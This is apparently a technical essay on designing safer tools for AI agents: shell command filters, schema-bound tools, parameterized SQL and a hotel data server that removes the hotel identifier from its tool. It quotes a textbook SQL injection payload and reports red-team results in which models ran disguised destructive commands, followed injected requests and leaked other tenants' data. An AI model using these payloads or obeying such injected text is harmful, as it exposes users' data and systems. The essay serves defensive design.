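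Ten of the eleven agents left a way for an injected command to run, but only five of these had a filter that failed. Three of the five matched patterns on the raw text. Opencode let through all 16 test commands, Goose let through 22 of 23, and Hermes failed on every type of rewriting despite having 30 patterns. Cline and Roo Code split the text into words before checking it and did much better. Three other agents had no filter and relied on the developer's approval, which a setting can turn off. The last two ran commands in a sandbox, which worked unless the user chose the documented option of running them directly on the computer.

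An attack also needed a model that would issue the command and some form of automatic execution. Sonnet 4.6 refused a blunt request to delete a file but issued the same command when it appeared to be part of routine project work. The survey is therefore better evidence about the filters than about how often attacks succeed in practice.

Cline's optional filter let through 8 of 13 test commands with a block-list alone, and 2 when an allow-list was added. This is probably because a block-list lets a command run if the checker fails to recognize it, while an allow-list holds it back. An allow-list still fails if the checker mistakes a dangerous command for a permitted one, or if the list includes a program with dangerous options. The two commands that got through exploited weaknesses of this kind.

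### Splitting the command into tokens

A better checker first splits the text into tokens, the words and operators the shell would recognize. It then separates chained commands and checks each one. If part of the text depends on something only the shell will work out, the checker can ask the developer.

Continue, the eleventh agent in the survey, checks arguments most thoroughly. It asks for approval whenever a token contains a variable, because the value is not yet known. It also applies its rules to nested commands and never rates the whole command as safer than the part inside. It asks before the output of one command goes into a shell or another language interpreter, and it compares the command with a list of destructive operations that no user setting can permit.

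Adversa AI gave this checker 21 test commands, and none got through without approval. In live tests of the default mode, Continue blocked or asked about all 24 commands. Some gaps remain, mainly in certain nested commands and in the options of ordinary programs.

The drawback is that Continue asks about many harmless commands, such as one that creates a folder named after the current month. A developer has to answer several such questions per session, which encourages people to turn them off. In the automatic mode of Continue's command-line version, 18 of the 24 commands ran or would have run, and Continue still blocked only the operations on its fixed list of destructive ones. Adversa AI estimates that an experienced engineer could rebuild the checker in two days, but it doesn't propose a way to avoid the extra questions.

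Codex uses tokens more strictly, as OpenAI's *Rules* explains. A rule is a list such as `["gh", "pr", ["view", "list"]]`, which covers viewing or listing proposed changes on GitHub. Codex compares the rule with the command's argument list one position at a time, and the inner brackets hold the choices for the third position, much like an enumerated value. Codex splits a longer script into separate commands only if the script consists of plain words joined by a few simple operators. If the script uses variables, wildcards, redirection or loops, Codex treats all of it as one call to the shell, which a rule for `gh` cannot match.

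These rules check only the beginning of a command, so anything may follow `gh pr view`. A rule that permits a program also permits any dangerous options it has. Codex's rules determine which commands may run outside its sandbox, so a carelessly written rule can let a command bypass the sandbox, which is the stronger protection.

Claude Code checks some options individually. It prompts the user before running `find` with an option that deletes files or starts a program, and before running Git in a different folder, because that folder may contain scripts that Git will run. It also prompts the user about any command it cannot fully parse. But the list of special cases is long and still growing. A recent version added a check for `ps`, which lists running programs, because some forms of one option also print environment variables, where developers often keep passwords.

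The vendors advise against relying on these checks. Anthropic calls patterns meant to limit a command's arguments "fragile", and warns that a rule denying a program is not a security boundary, because the same program can be started in other ways. Visual Studio Code's *Manage approvals and permissions* calls automatic approval of terminal commands "a best-effort convenience, not a security boundary". One reason is that the editor uses the grammar of the bash shell to parse commands for two other shells, zsh and fish. GitHub's draft *Bash Command Parser Specification*, which covers the parser behind its Copilot permissions, forbids developers to treat the parser's output as proof that a command is safe, and requires them to refuse any command the parser cannot identify.

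New mismatches between checker and shell keep turning up, even in checkers that split the text properly. *Coding-Agenten* (Cornelißen, 2026) describes five advisories that appeared between October 13 and 16, 2026. Two, on Mistral Vibe and Roo Code, concern commands that the checker read differently from the shell, and both are rated 8.8 out of 10 for severity. Mistral had fixed its agent a month earlier, but Roo Code's developers had stopped work on theirs in May, so its users will not get a fix. The other three have different causes. Junie CLI and ZCode could start programs named in a project's configuration files, and the Python version of Anthropic's Claude Agent SDK passed on a session identifier that another program could read as an option, much as in the Git server.

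### Starting programs without a shell

A developer can avoid the mismatch by removing the shell. Each permitted program gets its own tool, and the model fills in the tool's arguments instead of writing a command. The developer's handler code checks these arguments against the schema, puts them in a list after the program's name, and asks the operating system to start the program with that list. Quotation marks, semicolons and dollar signs inside an argument have no special meaning, because no shell reads them. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-461* (2026), an advisory on the agent framework PraisonAI, also recommends passing commands as argument lists instead of raw strings.

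Removing the shell does not solve the problem with options. Most of the systems that Trail of Bits examined already ran their commands without a shell, but they let the model write the options. The developer therefore also needs a schema listing the permitted options for each program, and the handler should write those options itself. For example, if the agent may choose how many lines of context a search shows, the schema accepts a whole number from 0 to 5, and the handler turns it into the corresponding option.

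Carelessly written handlers have the same weakness as the Git server. One of the three products that Trail of Bits broke into had a separate handler for each program, but one handler put the model's search text where the program could read it as an option. The usual fix is to put two hyphens (`--`) before the text, which tells many programs to treat everything after them as plain values. Trail of Bits considers handlers significantly better than lists of safe commands but less safe than a sandbox, and recommends a sandbox as the main protection.

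### A search command turned into a tool

Suppose a coding agent has a tool called `run_command(command)` and uses it to search a project:

```
rg parse_date src | head -n 20
```

The program `rg`, short for ripgrep, finds every line in the `src` folder that contains `parse_date`. The vertical bar is a pipe, which passes the results to `head`, and `head` keeps the first 20 lines. A narrow tool for the same job could look like this:

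```json
{
  "name": "search_code",
  "description": "Find lines that contain the given text.",
  "parameters": {
    "pattern":     { "type": "string", "minLength": 1, "maxLength": 200 },
    "directory":   { "type": "string", "enum": ["src", "tests", "docs"] },
    "max_results": { "type": "integer", "minimum": 1, "maximum": 100 }
  }
}
```

The agent now calls `search_code` with `parse_date`, `src` and 20. The handler checks the three values and builds this list:

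```python
["/usr/bin/rg", "--no-config", "--fixed-strings",
 "--line-number", "--", pattern, directory]
```

Only the last two items come from the model. The full path in the first item prevents the agent from substituting a program of the same name from the project folder. `--no-config` stops ripgrep from taking options from a configuration file, which a different tool could have written. `--fixed-strings` makes ripgrep look for the exact text, and `--line-number` adds line numbers to the results. The two hyphens let the agent search for a pattern that begins with a hyphen, because ripgrep does not treat anything after them as an option.

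The handler also has to confirm that `directory` is inside the project, in case another tool has replaced the folder with a link to somewhere else. Ripgrep can limit the number of matches per file but not in total, so the handler counts the results itself and stops at `max_results`. It should report when it has left some out, or the agent may conclude that a function appears in 20 places when it appears in 200.

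`pattern` is still a free-form string, but ripgrep only compares it with the text in the files, so it never reaches an interpreter.

The agent can no longer pipe results into another program, for example to count the matches in each file and sort the files by that number. It could read the matches and do the counting and sorting itself, but this takes more text and fails when there are more than 100 matches. It also can't use unusual options, such as searching only files of a certain type. If it needs a program without a handler, it has to wait for a developer to write a handler.

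Developers can restore the most common uses by adding an enumerated file type or a separate counting tool. The rare uses are harder to restore because there are so many of them and each is hardly worth its own tool. A sensible compromise is to let narrow tools run without approval and keep a shell for everything else, either with approval for each command or inside a sandbox. `search_code` then only needs to handle enough of the routine searches that the developer sees few approval requests and has time to read them. Neither Adversa AI nor Trail of Bits measured how many tasks an agent fails without a shell, so the size of the loss is uncertain.

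Narrow tools can also make an agent more reliable. *Building an Internal Coding Agent at Zup* (Pinto, Camargo and colleagues, 2026) describes CodeGen, an agent that developers at the Brazilian company Zup use every day. Its editing tool takes a file name, the text to find and the replacement text. The team chose this design because models that rewrote whole files tended to cut them short or leave parts out. They also found that improving the tools' descriptions and arguments helped more consistently than changing the prompts, though the paper gives no figures.

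### What a schema can and cannot check

A schema is good at refusing values of the wrong form. For `search_code`, the checks work as follows:

| Check | Example of a refused call |
|---|---|
| Type | `max_results` is the word "all" |
| Range | `max_results` is 5,000 |
| Length | `pattern` has 10,000 characters |
| Membership | `directory` is a system folder outside the list |
| No extra arguments | the call adds an argument called `options` |

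*AGENTSEC02-BP02 Validate tool inputs and outputs*, AWS's guidance for agent developers, recommends all of these. It warns against checking only what users type while trusting the values the model produces. Some services can force a model to produce only calls that fit the schema. This prevents many errors early, but AWS still recommends that the tool check each call, because a schema can't express some limits.

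One such limit is a relationship between arguments, such as a start date having to come before an end date. Others depend on facts outside the call, such as whether a file still exists, or on a company's rules, such as the largest payment an agent may make. AWS assigns these limits to further layers of ordinary code and fixed policies. They are still exact conditions, so a program can test them reliably once someone has written them down.

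Checking what a call means in its context is much harder. A search for "password" in `src` satisfies every condition in the table. A developer might request it to find passwords left in the code by mistake, and an attacker might request the same search, with identical arguments, to steal them. Similarly, a schema can ensure that a payment is a positive number below the limit, but not that the user wanted to pay that amount to that person.

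### Blocking one tool while another does the same

Pinto and colleagues concluded from building CodeGen that a restriction has to cover every tool that can produce the restricted effect. If they blocked direct deletion of files but left the shell unrestricted, the agent could delete the same files with a shell command.

Zup kept the shell in CodeGen because the agent needed it to run tests, build programs and use Git. Administrators can block the shell entirely or block particular commands through a configuration file. Developers can require approval for each command, and CodeGen records everything it runs. The list of blocked commands probably has the weaknesses that Adversa AI found in other block-lists. Requiring approval is stronger, but developers at Zup tended to switch to the autonomous mode as they came to trust the agent.

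The same problem affects rules for files and web addresses. Anthropic suggests blocking download programs in the shell and letting Claude Code fetch pages through a separate tool that accepts only listed domains. The separate tool is not enough on its own, because a shell that can still run a download program can reach any address. Similarly, a rule against reading a file applies to Claude Code's built-in file tools and the shell commands it recognizes, but not to a Python script that opens the file itself. For developers who need to stop every program from reading the file, Anthropic points to the sandbox, where the operating system enforces the limit however the command is written.

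## Database tools: from free SQL to parameterized queries

A database tool that accepts SQL text has much the same weakness as a shell tool, since an interpreter runs whatever the model writes. But databases, unlike shells, have long let developers fix the structure of a command before any outside value arrives.

### Three tools for one sales database

Suppose a camping equipment shop keeps its sales in a table called `orders`. Each row records the customer, the product and its category, the region, the sales channel, the year, the month and the amount. The shop wants an agent to answer questions from its staff, and its developer considers three tools.

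| Tool | Example of a call | Who writes the SQL |
|---|---|---|
| `run_sql` | `run_sql("SELECT SUM(amount) FROM orders")` | the model |
| `customer_orders` | `customer_orders("Maria Lopez", 2026)` | the developer, in advance |
| `sales_report` | `sales_report("revenue", "month", region="north")` | the handler, from parts that the developer wrote |

An agent with `run_sql` can use the data to answer any question it covers. The agent can also delete the table if the connection allows it. Large vendors offer such tools. For example, Google Cloud's *MCP Tools Reference* documents one called `execute_sql` for the data warehouse BigQuery, and one of the sample queries trains a machine-learning model.

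`customer_orders` runs one stored query and fills in a name and a year. For `sales_report`, which takes no free-form strings, the agent picks a measure, a grouping and some filters from fixed lists, and the handler builds the query.

### How binding keeps a value out of the query's structure

The careless way to write `customer_orders` is to join the customer's name into the text of the query. This fails even with honest input, because the apostrophe in a name like O'Brien ends the quoted text early. An attacker can use the same effect deliberately. PAIML's *SQL Safety and Injection Prevention* gives the textbook example of a "name" that reads `' OR '1'='1`. Joined into the shop's query, it produces this:

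```sql
SELECT product, amount FROM orders
WHERE customer = '' OR '1'='1'
```

The condition now has two halves, and the second is always true, so the database returns every customer's orders. Part of a value has become part of the command, which is called SQL injection.

A parameterized query prevents it by separating the two. The developer writes a placeholder where the value belongs:

```sql
SELECT product, amount FROM orders
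WHERE customer = $1
```

The database then works in this order:

1. It receives the query text with the placeholder still in it.
2. It parses the text into a structure: read two columns from `orders`, and keep the rows where `customer` equals a value that will arrive later.
3. It receives the value separately, as data.
4. It puts the value into the reserved place and runs the query.

Filling in the value is called binding, and a query that the database has parsed in advance is a prepared statement. The database has already parsed the query when the hostile name arrives, so it looks for a customer whose name is those 11 characters, apostrophes included, and finds none. The same query returns O'Brien's orders correctly.

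This protection is much stronger than the checks on shell commands because it doesn't depend on recognizing dangerous input. The agent also loses nothing, since the tool accepts every name it accepted before.

However, binding doesn't limit which rows a value can match. If the stored query searches for similar names with SQL's `LIKE` operator, a bound percent sign matches every customer. A correctly spelled name returns that person's orders whether or not the user is allowed to see them. Binding also protects only the query that uses it. If another tool stores a customer's comment unchanged in the database, the comment can still do damage when a program inserts it into a new query without binding it, or when an agent reads it as an instruction.

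### Why table and column names need fixed choices

The documentation for Google's *postgres-sql* explains that a placeholder can stand for a value but not for the name of a table or column. The database parses and plans a query before filling in the placeholders, and to do this it has to know which table the query concerns, whether the columns exist and what types they have. If a developer writes `SELECT $1 FROM orders` and binds the word "amount", the database returns the word "amount" once for every order.

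A tool that lets the agent choose a column therefore has to put a name into the query text before the database parses it. The safe way is to keep the model's own words out of that text. In `sales_report`, the agent's choice only selects an entry from a list that the developer wrote:

```python
MEASURES  = {"revenue": "SUM(amount)", "orders": "COUNT(*)"}
GROUPINGS = {"region": "region", "month": "order_month"}

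column = GROUPINGS[group_by]
total  = MEASURES[measure]
sql = f"SELECT {column}, {total} FROM orders WHERE category = $1 GROUP BY {column}"
```

If the agent sends anything not in the list, the lookup fails and no query runs. The category is an ordinary value, so the database binds it. Starburst's *Parameterized query tools usage examples* shows a commercial version of this design, in which a tool's parameters can be constants from an allowed list, checked references to columns, or references to functions.

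AnythingLLM, an application for chatting with documents and databases, lacked such a check. Its SQL agent could look up a table's columns, and it supplied the table's name as a free-form string. According to MITRE's *AnythingLLM has SQL Injection in Built-in SQL Agent Plugin* (2026), versions up to 1.11.1 inserted this string directly into a query in the connectors for all three supported databases (MySQL, PostgreSQL and Microsoft SQL Server). Anyone who could use the agent could therefore run arbitrary SQL on a connected database. The advisory rates the flaw 7.7 out of 10, high severity.

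HackerNoon's *A 56000 Star AI App Shipped With a Textbook SQL Injection Flaw* (2026), written by the researcher who found the flaw, reports that the same function checked another argument, the database identifier, against a list of configured connections. The researcher suspects that the developers did not check the model's choice of table because they thought of the model as a trusted part of their own program. Of 17 attacks tried on the three connectors, 15 worked.

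In two of the three connectors, the developers could have bound the table name as a parameter. PostgreSQL and SQL Server keep a catalog that lists every column with its table's name, and AnythingLLM searched this catalog for rows with a matching name, so the name was a value rather than an identifier. Only the MySQL connector used a command that needs the name as an identifier. There, a developer can either search MySQL's catalog in the same way or first check the name against the database's list of tables. The company behind AnythingLLM fixed the flaw with a parameterized query within two weeks of the report.

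Fixing the table-name flaw restricted the agent less than the severity score might suggest, because AnythingLLM had a second tool that ran any SQL the model wrote. Its description included an instruction to use only queries that read data, but HackerNoon reports that the code neither checked this nor used a read-only connection. An injected instruction blocked at the table name could still use the second tool.

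### Google's MCP Toolbox

Google's MCP Toolbox for Databases is an open-source server that lets developers define database tools in a configuration file. Its first stable version came out on April 10, 2026, and Google's *MCP Toolbox* lists PostgreSQL, MySQL, Oracle, MongoDB and Snowflake among the databases it supports. The shop's stored query could look like this:

```yaml
kind: tool
name: customer_orders
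type: postgres-sql
source: shop-db
statement: |
  SELECT product, amount FROM orders
  WHERE customer = $1 AND order_year = $2
  LIMIT 50
description: List one customer's orders in a given year.
parameters:
  - name: customer
    type: string
    description: Full name of the customer
  - name: year
    type: integer
    description: Year of the orders
    minValue: 2022
    maxValue: 2026
```

The agent sees the tool's name, its description and the two parameters. The Toolbox checks the year against the limits, and the database binds both values to a prepared statement. The last line of the SQL limits the result to 50 rows, and the agent cannot change this limit because it isn't a parameter.

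The Toolbox has a separate feature for table and column names, called template parameters. It inserts these into the text before the database prepares the statement, so they can change the query's structure. The Toolbox documentation page *Tools* says this makes them prone to SQL injection and recommends that developers use ordinary parameters instead. ScyllaDB's *MCP Toolbox for Databases* advises ScyllaDB users to use template parameters only where the name has to vary.

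A developer who needs a template parameter can restrict it with `allowedValues`, which limits it to a list of values, or with `escape`, which puts quotation marks or similar delimiters around it so that the database reads it as a single name. The allow-list is better where it is practical, because a properly delimited name can still refer to a column of home addresses. But `allowedValues` also accepts patterns, and a loose pattern can admit hostile text. A copy of the project's change log on Glama dates both settings to version 0.18.0, from October 23, 2025.

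The Toolbox can also fill in a parameter from the user's login. If the shop's customers could talk to the agent directly, `customer_orders` should return only their own orders. To ensure this, the developer marks the customer's identifier as an authenticated parameter. The application sends the Toolbox an ID token, a signed record of who has logged in, and the Toolbox reads the identifier from it, as Google's *AuthServices* explains. The agent no longer supplies the identifier, so injected text cannot make it request another customer's orders. However, this requires a token from a logged-in user, which an agent running overnight under a shared company account doesn't have.

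These protections apply only to the tools a developer defines this way. The Toolbox also includes ready-made tools, and its first stable version added one that runs arbitrary queries in the language of the search engine Elasticsearch, according to Google's release notes (2026).

The configuration file also needs protection. It contains SQL that the server will run, so it belongs on the list of places from which an interpreter takes instructions. A coding agent that can edit this file can add a tool containing any SQL statement, just as it could write a command into Git's settings.

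### Why a read-only mode is not enough

Early database servers for agents often accepted free SQL but were described as read-only. Anthropic's reference server for PostgreSQL was one of them, but Datadog Security Labs found that it allowed arbitrary SQL statements. According to Draxlr's *MCP Servers for SQL*, the server put each query inside a read-only transaction, a group of statements that the database handles together. It didn't check whether the text contained more than one statement, so further statements could escape the read-only protection.

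PostgreSQL cannot prepare text that contains several statements, so preparing the query would have closed this gap. Anthropic had archived the server in May 2025, but people were still downloading it about 21,000 times a week almost a year later. According to Draxlr, the penetration tester Maximilian Hildebrand reported in July 2026 that he could get around the read-only mode of 14 SQL servers for agents, and the faults fell into three repeating patterns. Anthropic's reference server for SQLite, a small database engine, had an ordinary SQL injection flaw. Trend Micro found the flaw after Anthropic had archived that server too, and reported that no patch was planned.

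Even a working read-only mode would only prevent changes to the data. The agent could still read every table the connection can access and pass the contents to another tool. On some databases, SQL can also read files on the server and run operating-system commands if the account has enough privileges, which would let the agent use `run_sql` for general computation.

Limits enforced by the database are more reliable than limits enforced by the server that passes SQL to it. In a security bulletin about its own PostgreSQL server for agents, AWS (2026) calls a dedicated database role the strongest control. A role is an account with its own permissions, which the database enforces no matter what SQL arrives. AWS warns against connecting as an administrator, because administrators bypass the rules that decide which rows each account may see. Forkast similarly advises operators of another product,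 Postgres MCP Pro, not to count on its restricted mode to contain SQL written by an agent.

Roles and narrow tools work well together. The shop could let the agent's role read only `orders`, and use the tools to limit which queries it can run on that table. A mistake in a handler would then expose the orders but not the payroll.

### How many questions a closed tool can answer

TianPan.co's *Tool Schema Design Is Your Blast Radius* (2026) argues for enumerated values wherever the choices are finite, and says they make a tool only slightly less flexible. That is surely right for a tool that changes an order's status, but a data agent can lose more flexibility because its users ask questions that nobody has listed.

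The number of different calls is easy to work out. If a tool has *m* measures, *g* groupings and *k* filters with *v*<sub>1</sub> to *v*<sub>*k*</sub> values, it accepts

*m* × (*g* + 1) × (*v*<sub>1</sub> + 1) × … × (*v*<sub>*k*</sub> + 1)

calls. The added ones cover a report without a grouping and filters that the agent leaves open.

Suppose `sales_report` offers six measures: revenue, number of orders, and the average, median, largest and smallest order. It can group by month, region, category or channel, and it can filter by four regions, eight categories, two channels and five years. The grouping and each filter are optional, so 29 listed options (six measures, four groupings and 19 filter values) allow 6 × 5 × 5 × 9 × 3 × 6 = 24,300 different calls. Some of these are pointless, such as grouping by region after filtering to a single region.

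If the developer replaces the year with a start date and an end date, there are 1,668,051 possible periods within the five years, and the number of possible calls rises to about 6.8 billion. But the agent still gets only totals and averages for groups of orders, so the number of possible calls is a poor guide to which kinds of question a tool can answer.

Several calls to `sales_report` can answer questions that a single call can't. To find out which region has grown fastest since last year, the agent can request revenue by region for both years and compare the results. But a manager might ask, "Which customers bought a tent last year and have ordered nothing since?" No series of calls to `sales_report` can answer that, because its results never include customers' names, but one `run_sql` query of moderate length can.

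The same restriction protects customers' privacy, though not completely. If only one person in the north bought a kayak in March, that group's revenue is the price that person paid. A safer handler would withhold totals for very small groups.

### What vendors measured

Companies had tools like `sales_report` long before they had agents. One example is the semantic layer, software that stores a company's definitions of its measures, such as whether revenue includes refunds, and generates SQL from them. An agent using one only has to pick the right measures and groupings.

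The company dbt Labs, which sells a semantic layer, compared it with free SQL. Ganz and Perigaud (2026), in *Semantic Layer vs. Text-to-SQL*, used 11 questions about a fictional insurance company and ran each one 20 times per model. With free SQL, the model received the whole database schema and wrote its own query. dbt Labs' *LLM Semantic Layer Benchmark* notes that three of the questions required links between tables that the semantic layer could not express. These are the percentages of correct answers on the original tables:

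| Questions | Free SQL, GPT-4 (2023) | Free SQL, Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Free SQL, GPT-5.3 Codex | Semantic layer, GPT-4 (2023) | Semantic layer, either newer model |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 8 that the layer covered | 26.9 | 62.5 | 51.2 | 83.1 | 100 |
| 3 that it did not cover | 48.3 | 70.0 | 100 | 0 | 0 |
| All 11 | 32.7 | 64.5 | 64.5 | 60.5 | 72.7 |

On the covered questions, the closed interface made the agent far more useful. Over all 11, its lead shrank to about eight points.

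Ganz and Perigaud then had a language model add three new tables, with matching definitions, so that the layer could answer every question. Sonnet 4.6 scored 98.2% with the layer and 90.0% with free SQL, and GPT-5.3 Codex scored 100% and 84.1%. Free SQL gained 20 to 25 points from the new tables alone. These scores somewhat overstate the layer's advantage, because the new definitions were made to fit the test questions. A company cannot do that for questions its staff have yet to ask. On the other hand, the test gave the model the whole schema, which a larger company could not do.

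Ganz and Perigaud write that the layer never silently returns wrong data. This is true of the SQL it generates, but a model can still pick the wrong measure. Sonnet scored 98.2%, so about four of its 220 runs failed, and Ganz and Perigaud do not report whether those runs ended in an error message or a wrong number.

Part of the benefit comes from the definitions and does not require a closed tool. *Semantic Layers for Reliable LLM-Powered Data Analytics* (Rumiantsau, 2026) tested three models writing free SQL with and without a short document explaining the business's terms. The document, not the choice of model, accounted for nearly all of the significant variation in the results. Cube, another seller of semantic layers, published the test materials. According to Cube's *semantic-layer-benchmark*, the document was about 4 kilobytes and raised accuracy by 17 to 23 percentage points on 100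 questions about a retail business.

Vendors of other products have reached different conclusions. Muller-Molina (2026) reports in *How PyDough Reached 100% Accuracy on dbt's Semantic Layer Benchmark* that the software company Bodo answered dbt's questions correctly in all 220 runs without a hand-built layer. Jacob Matson of the database company MotherDuck got 94% to 95% on a well-known set of 500 questions by giving models only the schema. In *The 7-Table Fallacy*, axiussdc accepts that result but doubts it applies to large companies' databases.

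Accuracy is therefore a weak reason to close the interface, and it will probably get weaker as models improve. The stronger reason is that closing it limits what the agent can reach. None of these tests measured that effect, because none included an attacker.

### Questions outside the predefined set

When a question fell outside dbt's semantic layer, the agent returned an error. dbt Labs' *Historical Comparison (2023 vs 2026)* confirms that the agent scored zero on those questions in every year and with every model. TextQL, a competitor, presents this as a basic constraint of the approach, because better models don't help when the layer cannot express the question.

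Ganz and Perigaud regard the error as an advantage because when free SQL fails, it tends to return a plausible wrong answer. Their results only partly support this. GPT-5.3 Codex with free SQL answered the three uncovered questions correctly in all 60 runs, so a refusal would have withheld 60 correct answers. But on the other eight questions it failed in 78 of 160 runs, and a manager reading the answers could not have told which ones to trust.

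A developer can respond to a refused question by extending the semantic layer. In dbt's test, this took three new tables and no handwritten code. But definitions in the layer become SQL, so someone should review each one before it takes effect, and the agent that answers questions should not be able to write them.

Ganz and Perigaud recommend falling back on free SQL for exploratory questions that the layer does not cover. Some developers go further, as Vercel did when it replaced most of its data agent's specialized tools with a shell. If the agent can fall back on free SQL by itself, the layer no longer protects against injected text, because an attacker only has to inject a question that the layer cannot answer. The shop could instead let the agent draft the query about tent buyers and have an employee run it. It could also let the query run automatically under a role that can read only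 a copy of `orders` without names and addresses. The copy would be enough to count the lapsed customers, but the manager who wants to write to them would still need an employee to run the query on the original table.

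## A hotel data server that stopped letting the agent name the hotel

Binding makes a database treat a hotel's number as a value, but it doesn't check whether the agent picked the right hotel. In *The Stochastic Deputy*, Baig, Gillani and colleagues (2026) studied this problem on a commercial server that keeps many hotels' data in one database. Three of the four researchers work for Fandaqah, which operates the server, so they had access to a production system but also a stake in how it performed.

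Most logins on the server cover only a few hotels, but logins for managers of a whole portfolio cover many more. An agent uses the login of the person it serves.

### Why a correct check still fails

The usual tool for fetching reservations is `get_reservations(hotel_id, limit)`. The server looks up which hotels the login covers and refuses the call if `hotel_id` is not among them. This is enough for an ordinary program, because its code determines which hotel it requests. An attacker would have to change the code or steal the login. But an agent's choice of hotel depends on everything it has read, including emails and the notes guests leave with their bookings.

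Baig and colleagues write *E*(*p*) for the set of hotels that the login of user *p* covers, and Rows(*t*) for the data of hotel *t*. Whoever steers the agent can then reach

Reachable(*p*) = ⋃<sub>*t* ∈ *E*(*p*)</sub> Rows(*t*),

which is all the rows of all the hotels on the login. Take an area manager whose login covers three hotels with 2,000, 3,000 and 5,000 reservations. The manager asks the agent about the first hotel, so the task needs at most 2,000 rows, but the agent's reach is 10,000. If a guest's note contains an injected request for the third hotel's reservations, the server checks the login, finds the third hotel on it and returns the data. The check has worked exactly as its developer intended.

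Baig and colleagues adapt Hardy's term and call the agent a "stochastic deputy", because a model can make different choices given the same input and receives instructions and data through the same channel. Writing for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues similarly in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* that language models are "inherently confusable". He doubts that prompt injection will ever have a fix like parameterized queries, which fixed SQL injection, and advises developers to constrain the system with safeguards that don't depend on a model.

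### A tool with no hotel argument

The redesigned tool is `get_reservations(limit)`. Its schema has no argument that selects a hotel, so the agent cannot express a request for a different one. The server still has to know whose data to return, and it gets this from the login:

1. An identity provider, the service that handles logins, issues a token that lists the user's hotels and signs it with a private key.
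2. The agent calls `get_reservations` and chooses only the number of rows.
3. The server verifies the signature and reads the hotels from the token. It ignores any other part of the request that claims to identify the user.
4. Code underneath the tools adds a filter for these hotels to the database query.

The server has to read the token carefully. During development, the researchers found that it accepted digits from other scripts, such as Arabic-Indic numerals, so group names that looked different to an administrator could give access to the same hotel.

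Other developers have made the same design choice. LangChain's *How to pass run time values to tools*, a guide for an agent framework, warns that letting the model control a user ID may be a security risk. LangChain's *InjectedToolArg* describes an annotation for such arguments. The framework leaves them out of the schema the model sees and fills them in when the tool runs. The authenticated parameters in Google's MCP Toolbox follow the same principle.

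Step 4 matters because the server has several dozen tools, and a developer who forgets the filter in one of them exposes every hotel's data without causing an error. Baig and colleagues describe two places to put the filter. The stronger version puts it in the database. The server's account can read only views, which are stored queries that already contain the filter, and any query that names an underlying table fails. In the weaker version, one module of the server builds every query and adds the filter. This prevents forgotten filters, but code that connects to the database without using the module can still read everything. The production server uses the weaker version because the stronger one requires changes to the live database. The researchers tried the stronger one only on a local copy.

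The filter also has to cover every table in a query, so the query builder adds it to each table it joins. A query might select one hotel's reservations correctly and then look up the guests' contact details in a second table. If a guest first stayed at a different hotel, that hotel may have created the guest's record. In the worst case the researchers found, 15.72% of the rows in one table pointed to another hotel's records, and every such record they inspected contained a name and a telephone number.

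### What agents did with and without the identifier

To test the effect of removing the argument, the researchers ran 373 trials with eight model configurations: Claude Opus 5, Gemini 3.1 Pro, GPT-5.4 mini, three tiers of GPT-5.6 and two small open models. The login gave access to three hotels, but each session concerned only one. The researchers counted a leak if the server's log showed that a tool had returned another hotel's data, regardless of what the agent reported.

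They compared three versions of the tool. The first had the hotel identifier, with a correct check. The second had no identifier. The third was the same as the first, but the agent also had a written rule never to retrieve another hotel's data, whoever asked for it.

In the most informative trials, the user made a plausible request for the same figures for a second hotel, saying they were preparing a comparison.

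| Tool | Trials with the plausible request | Trials in which the agent visibly tried to get the data | Trials in which the tool returned it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Identifier present | 41 | 26 | 26 |
| Identifier removed | 56 | 24 | 0 |
| Identifier present, with a written rule | 33 | 0 | 0 |

When the identifier was present, the server fulfilled all 26 attempts. All 15 trials without an attempt used GPT-5.6, which declined every time. Some of the other agents noticed that the request might exceed their authorization but retrieved the data anyway.

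With the identifier removed, the server never accepted a call that named another hotel. The 24 attempts are a minimum, because in some trials the agent's software could not send such a call, so there was nothing to count. Twelve agents still got another hotel's data without using the tool, because the test harness had left the session's scope writable.

A designer therefore has to protect the scope as well as remove the argument. In the production system, the signature protects the scope because any change to the token makes it invalid. The researchers sent the production server seven requests with missing, altered or unsigned credentials, and it refused them all. They did not test whether it accepts a valid token. A signature doesn't stop anyone from reusing a valid token, however. *Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) points out that most access tokens work for whoever holds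 them. It is safer to keep the token in the program around the model, where none of the agent's tools can read or replace it.

### Why the two zeros differ

Removing the identifier and adding a written rule both resulted in zero leaks through the tool, but the rule's result is only an estimate of how often models will follow it. With no leaks in 33 trials, the true leak rate could still be as high as 10%, based on the researchers' 95% confidence interval. A rule that failed once in a thousand requests would pass a 33-trial test about 97% of the time, yet on a server handling 10,000 such requests a day, it would leak ten times a day on average.

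Only 18 of the 33 trials, those with Claude, show the rule's effect. The other 15 used GPT-5.6, which had declined the plausible request without any rule. For the Claude trials alone, the same statistical method gives an upper limit of about 18%. The effect was large, since Claude had retrieved the data in all 18 trials without the rule. But the researchers did not test the rule on Gemini, GPT-5.4 mini or the small open models.

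The result for the tool without an identifier was zero because the agent cannot name another hotel in a valid call, so further trials would give the same result with any model. The design can still fail if the server's code has a bug or an administrator puts the wrong hotel in a token. People can look for such mistakes by reading and testing the code, and switching to a new model does not reintroduce the ones they have fixed. Removing the identifier therefore provides structural assurance, which is stronger than the behavioral assurance of a written rule.

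Behavior also varies a great deal between models. In other trials, the researchers gave agents openly malicious instructions, either in the user's message or in a guest's note. With the identifier present and no written rule, the results were:

| Model | Leaks | Trials |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 0 | 26 |
| GPT-5.6 (three tiers) | 0 | 30 |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 18 | 36 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 27 | 36 |
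| Two small open models | 1 | 4 |

Two sets of OpenAI models gave opposite impressions. A hotel company that tested its agent with one model and then switched to another, perhaps to save money, could lose its protection without changing any of its own code.

Claude resisted every malicious instruction but complied with the plausible request every time unless it had the written rule. Zhang, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Act on Your Behalf, Beyond Your Authorization*, found a similar pattern in a larger test of 286 tasks and 6,864 runs. Agents did something their user had not authorized in 19.2% of runs. The rate was 23.5% under ordinary pressures and 17.6% under malicious injections. Across 24 combinations of model, reasoning effort and agent software, it ranged from 10.5% to 26.6%, and more reasoning made almost no difference overall. Training a model to recognize attacks may not help much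 with requests that don't look like attacks.

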